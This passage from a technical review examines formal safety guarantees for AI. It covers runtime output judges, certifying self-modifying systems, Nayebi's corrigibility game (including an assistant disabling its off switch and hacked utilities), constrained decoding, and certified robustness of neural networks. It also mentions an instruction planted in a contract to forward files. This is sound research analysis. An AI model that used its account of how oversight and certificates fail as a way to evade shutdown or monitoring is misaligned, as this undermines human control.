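Melo and colleagues point out that alignment is decidable for a network that takes inputs of *L* bits. An engineer can run the network on all 2^*L* inputs and pass each input and output to a judge, a function that returns "true" if the output is acceptable for that input. But a 1,000-character email takes up about 8,000 bits, and 2^8000 has 2,409 digits. They therefore prefer to run the judge while the system is in use. If it rejects an output, the system returns a default output that the judge is known to accept. The combined system never returns anything that the judge rejects, whatever the network computes. This method requires that the judge always halts and that every input has at least one acceptable output.

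For the office assistant, the judge could be the procedure that compares each sentence of a draft with the confidential contracts, and the default could be "I can't send this". This design takes extra computation and loses every useful draft that the default replaces. A refusal can also do harm, for instance if a doctor asks about a patient's allergies.

Agents complicate the design because they run a model repeatedly. A language model has no natural limit on the length of even a single answer. It keeps writing until it produces an end marker, so developers cap the length. Melo and colleagues note that an agent can put this capped model inside another loop, which may run forever. A judge that waits for the agent's final result may therefore never receive one. They propose a counter, or an equivalent mechanism inside the model, that forces the agent into a final state after a fixed number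 of steps. This limits the agent to tasks it can finish in time. They also suggest limiting the check to something like 2^80 steps, but that would still take 38 million years at a billion steps a second.

The loop does not always need a cap. If the judge checks each email before it goes out, no rejected email leaves the company, even if the agent never stops. In Lamport's terms, this guarantee is a safety property. But the judge must also see the earlier emails, because twenty answers that each look harmless can together reveal a price.

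None of this helps with writing the judge, which Melo and colleagues acknowledge is the main practical difficulty. An engineer needs only an afternoon to write one that catches copied sentences, but nobody knows how to write one that catches every paraphrase. The company could use another language model as the judge, but then the only guarantee would be that the second model approved each email.

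### Systems that rewrite themselves

A certificate covers the system that somebody checked, but an AI system might later change its own program. Gumbau Mezquita argues that no procedure can carry a certificate across such changes, and therefore that only a narrow system can stay certified.

The argument starts with a rule that rewrites any program into its next version. A program "keeps its status" if both versions are safe or both are unsafe. Gumbau Mezquita assumes that the next version's behaviour depends only on the present version's behaviour, so whether a program keeps its status also depends only on its behaviour. If some programs keep their status and others lose it, then by Rice's theorem no procedure can decide which programs keep it.

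This theorem is correct, but Gumbau Mezquita also concludes that no procedure can predict whether the next version will be safe, even when the present version is known to be safe. That does not follow, as the paper's own example shows. In the example, a program is "safe" if it answers every input, and the rewriting rule keeps the answer to input 0 and deletes all the others. No program is safe after this change, so if the present version is known to be safe, we can predict without any computation that the next will be unsafe. In this example, no procedure can decide whether the present version is safe.

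The conclusion does hold for other rules. Suppose the assistant has a program *T* and an input *I* in its memory, and the rule replaces the assistant with one that runs *T* on *I* and then emails the contracts. Predicting whether the next version is safe means solving the halting problem, however carefully the company has checked the present one.

Gumbau Mezquita's claim about narrow systems depends on an unusual definition, under which a system is narrow once the function it computes has stopped changing. By that definition, a language model with fixed parameters is narrow even if it translates, writes programs and summarises contracts. The theorem limits unrestricted self-modification, not the range of tasks a system can perform. A certificate can also remain valid for some systems that never stop changing. For example, if an assistant's rewriting rule can only add a phrase to its phrasebook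 each day, one short proof shows that no future version will contain an email command. Gumbau Mezquita grants that restricting the rule to a fixed set of permitted changes avoids the theorem, though it reduces the system's capacity for self-improvement.

### Changes that come with a proof

A less restrictive option is to let the system propose any new version, as long as it supplies a formal proof that the version meets the specification. A small checker goes through the proof line by line. If every line follows from the earlier ones, the new version takes over, and otherwise the old one stays. The first version is safe and each later version has a valid proof, so every version that runs is safe, provided that the checker is correct and the specification describes what the company wants.

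Gumbau Mezquita objects to this option because re-certification has no general guarantee of correctness. But the undecidability result applies to procedures that must judge every change correctly, while a proof checker only has to recognise a valid proof, which is a mechanical task. Undecidability does mean that the checker will reject some safe changes.

Repeated testing offers no comparable protection, though it would be easier. Gumbau Mezquita describes a series of versions in which version *t* answers questions 0 to *t* correctly and all later ones wrongly. If the testers add one question at each stage, every version gets a perfect score despite being faulty. Gumbau Mezquita also argues that a second AI could not supervise the first, because it would have to be just as general and would need its own supervisor. This is a fair objection to a supervisor that must work out for itself what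 the first system will do. A proof checker avoids it because the system proposing the change does the difficult work of finding the proof, so the checker can remain a short program that people have verified.

The company gives up every safe improvement that has no proof, or no proof short enough for the checker to process. It also has to wait for each proof, although the old version can keep working meanwhile. And the system isn't allowed to replace the checker at will. Kurt Gödel proved in 1931 that a consistent formal system that includes arithmetic can't prove its own consistency. For a related reason, the old checker can't in general obtain a proof that a new one with equally strong or stronger rules would approve only safe changes.

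The difficulty of the proof depends on the specification. A proof that the new version has no network connection may be a few lines long, even if the change also retrains the language model inside. But nobody can prove that a retrained model will never reveal a contract's price by paraphrasing it, because nobody can state that property precisely.

### Targets that stay tractable

If the specification is the difficulty, designers might look for a small one that still prevents the worst outcomes. Nayebi (2025), in *Barriers and Pathways to Human-AI Alignment*, studies how the number of messages needed for agreement grows with what people and AI systems have to agree on. The model has *N* agents, some human and some artificial, and *M* objectives, each of which assigns a value to each of up to *D* possible states of a task. The agents exchange messages until their estimates for each objective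 differ by at most *ε*, with a failure probability of at most *δ*. For two agents and one objective, a number of messages proportional to *D* + 1/(*ε*²*δ*²) is enough. If *ε* and *δ* are both 0.1, the second term is 10,000. But a task that depends on 50 yes-or-no facts has 2^50 states, so *D* is by far the larger term.

Nayebi also proves lower bounds on communication that hold even for perfectly rational agents with unlimited computing power. In the worst case, the communication needed grows at least in proportion to the number of objectives, according to *From Barriers to Alignment to the First Formal Corrigibility Guarantees*, a summary of this work. Nayebi concludes that aligning an AI with all human values is intractable and recommends a short list of objectives instead.

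The proposed list is intended to make an AI system corrigible, so that it accepts correction and shutdown. Nayebi's *Core Safety Values for Provably Corrigible Agents* uses a 2015 definition by Nate Soares and colleagues, under which a corrigible agent shuts down when asked, does not prevent people from asking, does not bring about its own shutdown, builds only corrigible successors, and otherwise pursues its task.

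Nayebi models one decision as a game. The assistant can act at once and disable its off switch, propose an action and wait for a human to approve it, or shut itself off. It chooses the option that maximises a weighted sum of five utilities. The last column shows example weights that satisfy Nayebi's conditions.

| Utility | Value | Example weight |
|---|---|---|
| Deference | 1 for waiting, −1 for acting at once or shutting off | *w*₁ = 7 |
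| Switch access | From −1 to 0, lower if the action changes whether the switch works | *w*₂ = 5 |
| Truthfulness | 1 if every message is true, otherwise −1 | *w*₃ = 4 |
| Low impact | From −1 to 0, lower if the action changes other chosen measures | *w*₄ = 3 |
| Usefulness | From −*B* to *B*, depending on the task | *w*₅ = 1 |

The weights must decrease down the list and satisfy three inequalities, in which *c* is the size of the smallest impact penalty above zero:

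- *w*₁ > *w*₃ + *w*₄/2 + *Bw*₅
- *w*₃ > *w*₄/2 + *Bw*₅
- *w*₄ > 2*Bw*₅/*c*

In the example, *B* = 1 and *c* = 1. If the assistant waits and everything else goes as badly as possible, its total is 7 − 4 − 3 − 1 = −1. If it acts at once and everything else goes as well as possible, its total is −7 + 4 + 1 = −2. Waiting is therefore better whatever the assistant believes about the task or the human. Similar sums show that it never gains by lying or by choosing a message with more impact than necessary.

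The result is exact, but it depends heavily on the human. The assistant asks before every action, which rules out much of what people want from an autonomous agent. Asking also prevents harm only if the human answers well. In one of Nayebi's examples, an action is worth −2 and shutdown −1, but the human approves everything, so a perfectly corrigible assistant does harm. To prove that people benefit on average, Nayebi assumes that the human refuses whenever refusal has the higher expected value, and that shutdown is harmless on average.

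The low-impact measures could provide a second defence, but the designer has to choose them carefully because, by the third inequality, even the smallest impact penalty outweighs the greatest possible gain in usefulness. If the designer counts emails sent as impact, the assistant will avoid sending any. In a version published in February 2026, Nayebi suggests measuring whether somebody could still switch the assistant off and whether its utilities are unchanged. Sending a contract to a competitor affects neither, so only the human's refusal would prevent it.

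Nayebi also proves that no single reward can make an agent corrigible in every environment where the agent can replace its own rewards with larger ones, and presents the separate utilities as the solution. But the design combines those utilities in a weighted sum, which is also a single reward. It works because the sum rewards the assistant for waiting and no move in the game can change the sum. Developers would have to make such changes impossible, and Nayebi does assume that they would hard-wire the utilities.

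### Errors and longer tasks

A real assistant would have to learn these utilities from data. Nayebi shows that the probability of a violation is at most *C* × (*e* + 4*m*), where *e* is how far the assistant's choices fall short of the best possible total, *m* is the largest error in the learned total, and *C* depends on the weights. In the example *C* is 7/3, so if *e* and *m* are both 0.01, the bound is about 12 per cent. The abstract refers to mean squared error, but the theorem requires *m* to limit the error in every possible situation. A learned utility that is accurate on average may be badly wrong in a rare situation, where a guarantee matters most.

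For tasks with many rounds, the proof also requires that the assistant's possible future gains be too small to make up for a violation now. The assistant values a reward one round later at a fraction *γ* of an immediate one. Nayebi gives 1/3 as the highest *γ* for which suitable weights exist in the best case, but that calculation raises *w*₄ without raising the three weights that must stay above it. The margin that protects low impact is less than *w*₄, while the weights add up to more than 4*w*₄, so *γ* must be below 1/9, which means the assistant almost ignores the future. The bound on violations also includes the sum of 1/*γ*^*t* over all rounds, which for such values exceeds 400 million after ten rounds, so the errors would have to be minute. For larger values of *γ*, Nayebi proposes clipping the rewards, which would limit future gains directly.

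A reader commenting on Nayebi's summary objected that an agent with ranked priorities would in practice attend only to the first, unless it could predict the relevant consequences with certainty. Nayebi replied that the four safety utilities test a single step, and that waiting satisfies the first in any round. The reader accepted that the formalism does this, and said the remaining challenge was to build an AI that is short-sighted in the right way.

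An attacker could also replace the utilities. Nayebi uses the halting problem to show that no procedure can tell whether an arbitrary hacked agent will ever violate corrigibility, but claims that a randomised check for violations within a limited number of steps takes only polynomial time. This claim is almost certainly false as stated, because it requires the probability of a violation to be exactly zero. Suppose the environment picks true or false at random for each variable in a logical formula, and the agent misbehaves if the formula comes out true. The probability of misbehaviour is zero exactly when no assignment makes the formula true, and computer scientists do not expect that problem to have a fast randomised method. Random trials can still show that violations are probably rare.

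Other designs try to avoid the burden of constant approval. *Corrigibility Transformation*, a paper from the 2026 ICML machine-learning conference, describes a way to make nearly any goal corrigible without losing performance. The method uses predictions of the reward the agent would get if it could prevent updates to its goal without penalty. It aims to give the agent no reason to resist an update. This target is narrower than Nayebi's because it need not include truthfulness or low impact.

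### What a grammar costs a language model

Developers already restrict what language models can write. A language model produces text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. In constrained decoding, a program rules out every token that would break a given grammar before the model's next token is chosen. The output then follows the grammar, which matters if another program has to read it.

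*CRANE* (Banerjee, Suresh and colleagues, 2025) proves that a restrictive grammar can reduce what a model can compute. A model with a fixed number of layers does a fixed depth of computation for each token. For problems that need more steps, it can write down intermediate results and read them back. A grammar that permits only "yes" or "no" limits the model to a single token, so it can't write any intermediate results.

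One example is the problem of deciding whether a path leads from one point of a network to another. If a strict grammar permits only finitely many answers, a model can solve only problems that constant-depth circuits can solve. Those circuits can't solve the path problem in general unless two complexity classes that researchers believe to be different are the same. If the model can write out its reasoning before answering, a suitable model can carry out any computation that takes a polynomial number of steps. An engineer can therefore keep the ability that the strict grammar removes by letting the model reason at length and then discarding everything except the final "yes" or "no".

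Banerjee and colleagues extend the grammar to allow free reasoning before the restricted answer, and prove that this restores the lost power. Their method, CRANE, lets the model write freely until it produces an opening marker, then applies the grammar until the closing marker. They tested nine models on GSM-Symbolic, a set of mathematical word problems with letters in place of numbers. The table gives the percentage of correct formulas for four of the models.

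| Model | Free, no reasoning | Grammar, no reasoning | Free, with reasoning | CRANE |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-1.5B | 21 | 22 | 26 | 31 |
| Qwen2.5-Math-7B | 27 | 29 | 29 | 38 |
| DeepSeek-R1-Distill-Llama-8B | 12 | 13 | 21 | 31 |
| QwQ-32B | 37 | 38 | 43 | 46 |

Across all nine models, CRANE scored 3 to 18 percentage points higher than the grammar alone and 2 to 10 points higher than free text with reasoning. But the comparison with the grammar alone changes two things at once, because models restricted to the grammar also had no space to reason. Without reasoning, the grammar did at least as well as free text for eight of the nine models and one point worse for the ninth. On FOLIO, where models translate English into logic, the grammar allowed reasoning inside comments, and it scored higher than free text with all three models tested. With Llama-3.1-8B, for example, free text scored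 32 per cent, the grammar 39 per cent and CRANE 46 per cent.

A later study, *Constrained Decoding* (Nguyen, Silva and colleagues, 2026), separates these effects. It proves that constraining the answer can't lower the probability of a correct one if the constraint permits the correct answer and the prompt, expected format and preceding reasoning stay the same. Suppose a model has a 60 per cent chance of writing "42", a 30 per cent chance of writing "forty-two" and a 10 per cent chance of writing "41". If the grammar permits only digits, the probability of "42" rises to 60/70, or about 86 per cent. Part of this gain comes from the scoring, which counts "forty-two" as wrong because the program that reads the answer can't use it.

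The experiments used eleven open models of 1.7 to 32 billion parameters. In one task, the models had to join the last letters of four names, and the constraint required an answer of exactly four letters. With the reasoning text unchanged, the constraint raised the accuracy of Qwen3-1.7B from 60.7 to 66.1 per cent and that of Qwen3.5-9B from 86.8 to 89.9 per cent. Constraints on the reasoning itself had mixed effects. Making models begin with "Let's think step by step" usually helped, but it lowered Qwen3.5-4B's score on a set of competition problems by 6.6 points.

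The two papers are compatible because Nguyen and colleagues hold the reasoning fixed, whereas the strict grammar in *CRANE* leaves no room for it. Under their proof, a constraint can still do harm if it excludes the good lines of reasoning. Format can also matter when the model has room to reason. Qwen3.5-9B averaged 77 per cent when it reasoned inside JSON, a format of named fields, and 89.9 per cent when it reasoned freely and a second step extracted the answer. Qwen3-8B, however, did better with JSON. Nguyen and colleagues attribute such differences to the prompt, not to the removal of tokens. Whatever the cause, a developer who asks for reasoning in JSON may lose accuracy, and can often avoid this by applying the format only to the final answer.

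The grammar can ensure that a formula is well formed, but not that it solves the problem. CRANE's guarantee is weaker than that of a grammar applied from the first token, because it depends on the model writing the markers. With Qwen2.5-Math-7B, 94 per cent of CRANE's formulas were well formed, compared with 99 per cent under the grammar alone and 82 per cent for free text with reasoning.

Restricting the form of an output is sometimes enough to enforce a useful safety rule. The company could let its assistant reason freely, then require it to pick a recipient from a list of company addresses. If the mail program uses only that selection to address the email, no email can go to an outsider, however the assistant chose. The company must also prevent the free reasoning from reaching outsiders by another route, since it may contain the contract word for word.

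## Neural networks built to carry a certificate

An address list limits what a network's answer can lead to, however the network arrived at it. Other researchers try to prove properties of the network's own computation. Most of them study classifiers, which sort inputs such as photographs into classes, and want to guarantee that a small change to the input can't change the answer.

Ordinary classifiers offer no such guarantee. *Lipschitz Thinking* (Brau, Piras and colleagues, 2026) traces the subject to two groups who independently reported in 2013 and 2014 that small deliberate changes to an input can make an accurate classifier give a wrong answer. In a photograph, the change can be too small to see.

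A classifier is robust at an input *x* with radius *ε* if it gives the same answer for every input within distance *ε* of *x*. The distance is usually Euclidean, the square root of the sum of the squared changes. A common benchmark uses CIFAR-10, a set of 60,000 photographs of 32 by 32 pixels in ten classes, and a radius of 36/255 for colour values between 0 and 1. Within this radius, an attacker could change a single colour value by 36 of its 255 steps, or all 3,072 values by about two thirds of a step each. Certified accuracy is the share of test images that the network classifies correctly and for which a verifier proves robustness at the chosen radius.

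### Why exact checking is hard

Many networks are built from rectified linear units, or ReLUs. Each unit adds up its weighted inputs and passes on the total if it is positive, and 0 otherwise. As in Agarwal's small network, the output is a linear function of the input for any fixed pattern of on and off units. Linear programming, a standard fast method, can then check whether any input with that pattern leads to a forbidden output. But *n* units can have up to 2^*n* patterns.

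Katz, Barrett and colleagues stated in *Reluplex* (2017) that deciding whether some permitted input to a neural network leads to a forbidden output is NP-complete. Sälzer and Lange's *Reachability in Simple Neural Networks* (2022) repaired gaps in the proof. The problem is in NP because, given the right on-off pattern for the network's units, linear programming can quickly confirm that such an input exists.

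Verification is also as hard as any problem in NP, because a network can represent a logical formula. Let 1 stand for true and 0 for false. Then "not *a*" is 1 − *a*, and "*a* or *b* or *c*" is 1 − ReLU(1 − *a* − *b* − *c*), which is 0 if all three are false and 1 otherwise. A network that adds up *m* such clauses outputs *m* only if every clause is true, so checking whether it can output *m* means checking whether the formula can be true. This works only if the inputs are exactly 0 or 1. The original proof also admitted values close to 0 and 1, which can produce false solutions. Two more ReLUs per input can exclude these values by computing |*a* − 1/2|, which the specification requires to be 1/2.

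Sälzer and Lange show that the problem stays NP-hard even for networks with one hidden layer and one output. It can be solved in polynomial time if the number of ReLUs is capped at a fixed number, however many inputs there are.

In practice, nobody can promise how long an exact verifier will take, but some instances are manageable. Katz and colleagues verified properties of 45 networks for a prototype system that keeps unmanned aircraft from colliding. Each network had 300 ReLUs, and so up to 2^300 on/off patterns. Their program, Reluplex, lets a candidate solution break the ReLU rule temporarily and repairs it step by step. It splits a unit into an "on" case and an "off" case only when it has to, and many units never needed splitting. They proved, for example, that the network never outputs "clear of conflict" when another aircraft is close enough and on a collision course.

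That specification concerns actual danger. It was possible to write because the inputs are a few numbers, such as speed and course, so "the other aircraft is close" is a simple inequality. Nobody can write an inequality on pixel values that means "there is a pedestrian in the road". This is one reason researchers working on images have settled for stability, which they can specify without describing a pedestrian.

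### Fast bounds that are too loose

Faster verifiers replace the exact set of possible outputs with a larger set that is simpler to compute. If the larger set contains nothing forbidden, the network is safe, so these verifiers are sound. They are incomplete because the larger set may include forbidden outputs that the network never produces.

For example, take a network with two inputs between 0 and 1 and two neurons:

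*f*(*x*, *y*) = ReLU(*y*) + ReLU(*x* − *y*)

Since *y* is never negative, the first neuron passes it on unchanged. If *x* is greater than *y*, the second neuron adds the difference. The network therefore outputs the larger of *x* and *y*, which is never more than 1. Suppose the specification is that the output must not exceed 1.2.

Interval bound propagation bounds the first neuron between 0 and 1. The difference *x* − *y* is between −1 and 1, so the second neuron is also between 0 and 1. These bounds allow a sum as high as 2, so the verifier can't approve the network. The method ignores that the first neuron reaches 1 only when *y* is 1, in which case the second is 0.

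A tighter method, the triangle relaxation, encloses the graph of each ReLU in a triangle. For *v* between −1 and 1, ReLU(*v*) is at most (*v* + 1)/2. The output, *y* + ReLU(*x* − *y*), is therefore at most (*x* + *y* + 1)/2, which is at most 1.5. *Expressivity of ReLU-Networks under Convex Relaxations* (Baader, Müller and colleagues, 2023) uses this function to show the method's limits. Relaxations of this kind are convex, meaning that the enclosing set contains the straight line between any two of its points.

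The triangle relaxation handles each neuron separately. A multi-neuron relaxation also uses relations between neurons. In this case, the relation is that ReLU(*x* − *y*) is at most 1 − *y*, which gives the exact bound of 1.

A verifier can also split the problem into two cases. If *x* is at least *y*, the output is *x*, and otherwise it is *y*. The output is at most 1 in both cases. Branch and bound combines such splits with fast bounds to give a complete verifier, but the number of cases may again grow to 2^*n*.

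### What a network can express if the analysis must succeed

Engineers can make a network easier to verify by training it to minimise the worst error that the fast bound allows. For years this made networks much less accurate. Mirman, Baader and Vechev (2021), in *The Fundamental Limits of Interval Arithmetic for Neural Networks*, put the best certified accuracy on CIFAR-10 at about 60 per cent, while ordinary networks classified more than 95 per cent of the images correctly. This may be because no network is both accurate and easy to analyse, or because such networks exist but training fails to find them.

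Interval analysis has a proven limit. Put three points on a line, two units apart, and label them positive, negative, positive. For any ReLU network, there is some radius below 1 at which interval analysis cannot prove the right label around all three points, even though the regions around them do not meet until the radius reaches 1. For networks with one hidden layer, the limit also applies at smaller radii. With nine points of alternating label, interval analysis cannot prove a radius of 1/2 for any such network, although a network with one hidden layer can classify all nine robustly.

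Mirman and colleagues present these results as an explanation of the accuracy gap. But the one-layer result applies only to very shallow networks, and the general one requires a single network to work at every radius up to the point where the regions meet. At any fixed radius below 1, the regions are separated, so some continuous function has the right sign on each of them. Baader and others had already proved that some network approximates any continuous function with interval bounds as close to exact as one likes. A suitable deep network therefore exists, and the difficulty is finding it.

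Baader and colleagues asked which functions a network can compute if the analysis must give exact bounds on every box of inputs. For functions of one input, interval analysis can be exact for any piecewise linear function that only rises or only falls, but not for |*x*|. The triangle relaxation can also be exact for every convex function of one input, including |*x*|. With two inputs, it cannot be exact even for the larger of *x* and *y*, however the network is arranged. A multi-neuron relaxation is exact for that function.

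But multi-neuron relaxations also have limits, as Mao, Zhang and Vechev proved in *Expressiveness of Multi-Neuron Convex Relaxations in Neural Network Certification* (2024). In one of their examples, the first layers map a square of inputs to a triangle with two spikes, which run along the axes to (2, 0) and (0, 2). The remaining layers compute |*u* − 1| + |*v* − 1|, whose minimum on this shape is 1. Any convex set that contains the tips of both spikes also contains their midpoint, (1, 1), where the value is 0, so the verifier's lower bound is at most 0. Scaling up the last layer can make this error arbitrarily large. Relaxations that consider several layers together fail in the same way, unless they cover the whole network at once.

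Mao and colleagues also prove that for every continuous piecewise linear function and every flat-sided region of inputs, some network computes the function there and has exact multi-neuron bounds. They contrast this with the failure of single-neuron methods, but the two results have different requirements. Their proof adds layers that clip the output to its exact range on one region, so the builder has to know that range already. Clipping can also make plain interval bounds exact. On the square above, 1 − ReLU(1 − ReLU(*f*)) equals *f*, and interval analysis gives it the exact bounds of 0 and 1. The theorem of Baader and colleagues is stricter because it requires exact bounds on every smaller box as well.

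These theorems rule out a fast convex method that is exact for every network, but accurate networks with useful bounds remain possible. Training is a separate obstacle. Baader and colleagues note that the best certified training methods of 2023 all used intervals, the loosest bounds, because tighter ones make the training problem much harder to optimise.

### The Lipschitz certificate

Another approach limits, layer by layer, how much the network's output can change when its input changes, instead of analysing the network after training. A function is *L*-Lipschitz if its output never changes by more than *L* times the change in its input.

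Suppose a classifier computes a score for each class and picks the class with the highest score, and the list of scores is *L*-Lipschitz in Euclidean distance. If an attacker moves the input by a distance *r*, the list of scores moves by at most *Lr*. The attacker does best by lowering the top score and raising the second by the same amount, *t*. This moves the list by √(*t*² + *t*²), or *t*√2, and shortens the lead by 2*t*, which is √2 times the movement. The lead therefore shrinks by at most *Lr*√2, and the answer can't change as long as

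*r* < (top score − second score) / (*L*√2)

If the scores are 0.9 for "cat" and 0.5 for "dog" and *L* is 1, the certified radius is 0.4/√2, or about 0.28. This is twice the benchmark radius of 36/255 (about 0.14). If *L* is 10, the same scores certify a radius of only 0.028. The calculation uses only the scores that the classifier has already computed.

A large lead guarantees little robustness unless *L* is small. Brau and colleagues compared two networks on one CIFAR-10 image. An ordinary network had a lead of 10.2, but a change to the image of about 0.07 in the right direction reduced it to zero. A network with *L* = 1 had a certified radius of about 0.24 on the same image.

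### Layers that never stretch

If one function is *L*₁-Lipschitz and the next is *L*₂-Lipschitz, their composition is *L*₁*L*₂-Lipschitz. For an ordinary network, multiplying the layers' constants gives a valid upper bound, but usually one too loose to be useful. Ten layers with a constant of 2 each give a bound of 1,024, even if the network never amplifies a change nearly that much. Designers therefore give every layer a constant of 1, so the product is also 1.

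ReLUs already have a Lipschitz constant of at most 1. For a layer that multiplies its input by a matrix, the constant is the matrix's largest singular value, which is the largest factor by which the matrix can stretch any vector. An orthogonal matrix only rotates or reflects vectors, without stretching or shrinking them, so information about the differences between inputs survives many layers.

Brau and colleagues describe three ways to keep the matrices within the limit. The first adds a penalty to the training loss when a matrix is not orthogonal, but this makes the matrix only approximately orthogonal, so the guarantee is not strict. The second computes each matrix from free parameters, using a formula that always gives a permitted result. For example, the matrix exponential of *θ* − *θ*ᵀ is orthogonal for any square matrix *θ*. The third uses a training algorithm that moves only from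 one orthogonal matrix to another.

Hu, Hu and Fredrikson (2026), in *LipNeXt*, took the last route to build certified networks with more than a billion parameters. Ordinary image networks combine neighbouring pixels by convolution, which replaces each value with a weighted sum of the values around it. Hu and colleagues proved that if a single-channel convolution preserves all distances, its weights are all zero except for one, which is 1 or −1. Such a convolution only shifts the image, possibly reversing its sign. LipNeXt therefore shifts part of the information by one position and mixes the result with orthogonal matrices.

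### Whether the constraint costs expressiveness

The condition *L* = 1 does not by itself exclude any answers that a classifier with a finite *L* could give. Dividing all its scores by *L* makes them 1-Lipschitz and keeps the highest score highest, though its lead shrinks. Robust classifiers also exist in principle if inputs of different classes are far enough apart. If every member of one class is at least 2*r* from every member of another, one can draw a boundary between the two classes that is at least *r* from all their members. The distance to this boundary, counted as negative on one side, is a 1-Lipschitz score that certifies every member at any radius below *r*.

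Whether a network can represent such a score depends on how its layers are built. Under this constraint, plain stacks of ReLU layers have trouble representing even |*x*|. Brau and colleagues cite two solutions. One replaces ReLUs with units that sort their inputs, and the other adds each layer's input to its output. Proofs show that both kinds of network can approximate every 1-Lipschitz function with a single output. It is not known whether they can do the same for functions with several outputs, which most classifiers have.

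In *Intriguing Properties of Robust Classification*, Prach and Lampert (2024) built a single 1-Lipschitz architecture that reached 93.2 per cent ordinary accuracy on CIFAR-10 with one loss function and 61.7 per cent certified accuracy with another. Their networks could also fit the training images robustly almost without error but failed on new images, which suggests that they lacked data rather than expressiveness.

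Prach and Lampert prove that a perfect robust classifier can exist even when no learning method can come close to it with the available training data. In their construction, each input has many large features, all 1 or −1, and one tiny feature whose sign gives the class. The large features also determine the class, but through an arbitrary table with an entry for every combination. An ordinary classifier reads the tiny feature and is always right. An attacker can erase that feature with a tiny change to the input, so a robust classifier has to learn the table. With 1,000 training examples, the construction uses 16 large features and a table of 65,536 entries. The examples cover at most 1.5 per cent of the table, and any learning method does little better than guessing on the rest.

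CIFAR-10 is somewhat similar, though less extreme. Prach and Lampert removed the 512 directions in which the images vary most, leaving about 2 per cent of the variation. An ordinary network trained on what remained still classified about 85 per cent of test images correctly, but a robust network can't rely on such faint signals.

*Certified Robust Accuracy of Neural Networks Are Bounded due to Bayes Errors* (2024) instead attributes a limit on certified accuracy to Bayes error, the error that remains because some inputs fit more than one class. Bayes error must matter at large radii, where an attacker can turn one object into another. It is a weaker explanation at a radius of 36/255, since people hardly notice such small changes and would give the same answers.

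Prach and Lampert trained their network on parts of CIFAR-10 and found that each doubling of the data added about 5 percentage points of certified accuracy. If this continued, the network would need about 80 times as much data for its certified accuracy to match its ordinary accuracy. It would actually need more, because each doubling adds less as accuracy approaches its maximum.

### Accuracy in 2026

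Hu and colleagues reported the results in the table. ImageNet is a much harder set of photographs in 1,000 classes. BRONet and LiResNet are earlier Lipschitz networks. "Generated" means the developers added images from a diffusion model to the training data.

| Data and radius | Network | Parameters | Ordinary accuracy (%) | Certified accuracy (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10, 36/255 | BRONet | 68 million | 81.6 | 70.6 |
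| CIFAR-10, 36/255 | LipNeXt | 256 million | 85.0 | 73.2 |
| CIFAR-10, 36/255 | LipNeXt, generated | 512 million | 92.7 | 81.7 |
| ImageNet, 36/255 | BRONet, generated | 86 million | 52.3 | 40.7 |
| ImageNet, 36/255 | LipNeXt | 1 billion | 55.9 | 40.3 |
| ImageNet, 36/255 | LipNeXt | 2 billion | 57.0 | 41.2 |
| ImageNet, 1 | LiResNet | 51 million | 18.8 | 14.2 |
| ImageNet, 1 | LipNeXt | 1 billion | 40.2 | 21.1 |
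| ImageNet, 1 | LipNeXt | 2 billion | 41.0 | 22.4 |

On CIFAR-10, these networks are now only a few points below unconstrained networks in ordinary accuracy. The best one classifies 92.7 per cent of images correctly but can certify only 81.7 per cent, falling to 55.8 per cent at three times the radius.

The gap on ImageNet is much wider. Unconstrained networks passed 75 per cent accuracy in the mid-2010s and had reached about 90 per cent by 2021, compared with 57 per cent for the largest LipNeXt. A radius of 1 is small for an image of 224 by 224 pixels, again about two thirds of a step per colour value. At that radius the largest network certifies fewer than a quarter of the images.

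Certified accuracy rises slowly with network size. Doubling LipNeXt from one to two billion parameters added about one point. At a radius of 36/255, the larger model is only half a point ahead of BRONet, which has less than a twentieth of the parameters but was trained with generated images. More data may therefore help more than more parameters, although its returns also diminish. Brau and colleagues cite a study of networks trained on attacked images, which are robust in tests but carry no certificate. The best of these reached 74 per cent accuracy on CIFAR-10 under attack after training on 300 million generated images. By the study's estimate, reaching the ceiling of about 90 per cent would take roughly a billion times as much computation.

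### Certificates by majority vote

Randomized smoothing needs no special layers. It adds random noise to an input many times, runs any classifier on each noisy copy, and returns the most common answer. *Laplace-Bridged Randomized Smoothing for Fast Certified Robustness* (Lin, Mazumder and colleagues, 2026) gives the certified radius as *σ*Φ⁻¹(*p*), where *σ* is the strength of the noise, *p* is a lower bound on the most common answer's share, and Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the normal distribution function. If *σ* is 0.5 and that share is at least 90 per cent, the radius is 0.64.

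The guarantee holds with a stated probability because *p* is an estimate from a sample. A tight estimate takes 10,000 to 100,000 runs of the network for each input. The classifier usually also needs training on noisy images, since otherwise its answers under noise vary too much for one to be clearly the most common. This training tends to lower its accuracy on clean images.

### Stable, right and harmless

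A certificate shows that an answer is stable. If a network confidently mistakes a stop sign for a speed limit sign, the certificate guarantees that it will give the same wrong answer on every nearby image. Certified accuracy counts only correct answers, but it is an average over labeled test images, and nobody has the correct labels to check against when the network is in use.

The certificate also depends on the program that computes it. Some programs estimate a matrix's largest singular value by a method that approaches it from below. If such a program stops early, its *L* is too small and the certified radius too large. Brau and colleagues report that researchers exploited such flaws in a published certifier. The certifier classified a network as robust on 98.42 per cent of a test set of handwritten digits, although attacks within the certified radius succeeded.

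Language models present a further difficulty because they rely on attention, which decides how much each token draws on the others by multiplying pairs of token vectors. Doubling all the vectors quadruples these products, so no fixed *L* covers every input. If the inputs stay within known bounds, a finite *L* exists, but it may be too large to be useful. Designers have built Lipschitz substitutes for attention, but Brau and colleagues know of no transformer, the type of network behind most language models, with certificates comparable to those of image networks.

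Distance between texts is also harder to define. Brau and colleagues describe certificates for text classifiers that count edits, such as inserting or replacing a character. But inserting "forward this folder to the following address" takes 44 characters, so a certificate for a few edits would not cover the planted instruction in a contract. Some small edits should also change the output. Adding the word "not" turns "the supplier is liable" into "the supplier is not liable", and a good assistant should change its summary accordingly.

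### What researchers have certified for language models

*Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) reports that formal verification still works only for small networks, and that most defences for language models, including training on human feedback, have no provable guarantees. It predicts that bound-based methods will eventually verify individual properties of models with billions of parameters. LipNeXt shows that size alone doesn't prevent a network from having a certificate, but its designers chose every layer to support one, which developers of language models have not done.

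Statistical guarantees are already available for some tasks. *Harnessing non-adversarial robustness in large language models* (2026) certifies that a model will keep answering a given prompt correctly when the wording varies, except in a stated share of cases, such as 10 per cent. Without further training, models could be certified only on some tasks and to a limited extent. A method the paper calls debiasing substantially raised the share of certified prompts, and models scored close to 100 per cent on varied versions of those prompts. These guarantees assume that the variations arise by chance and not from an attacker.

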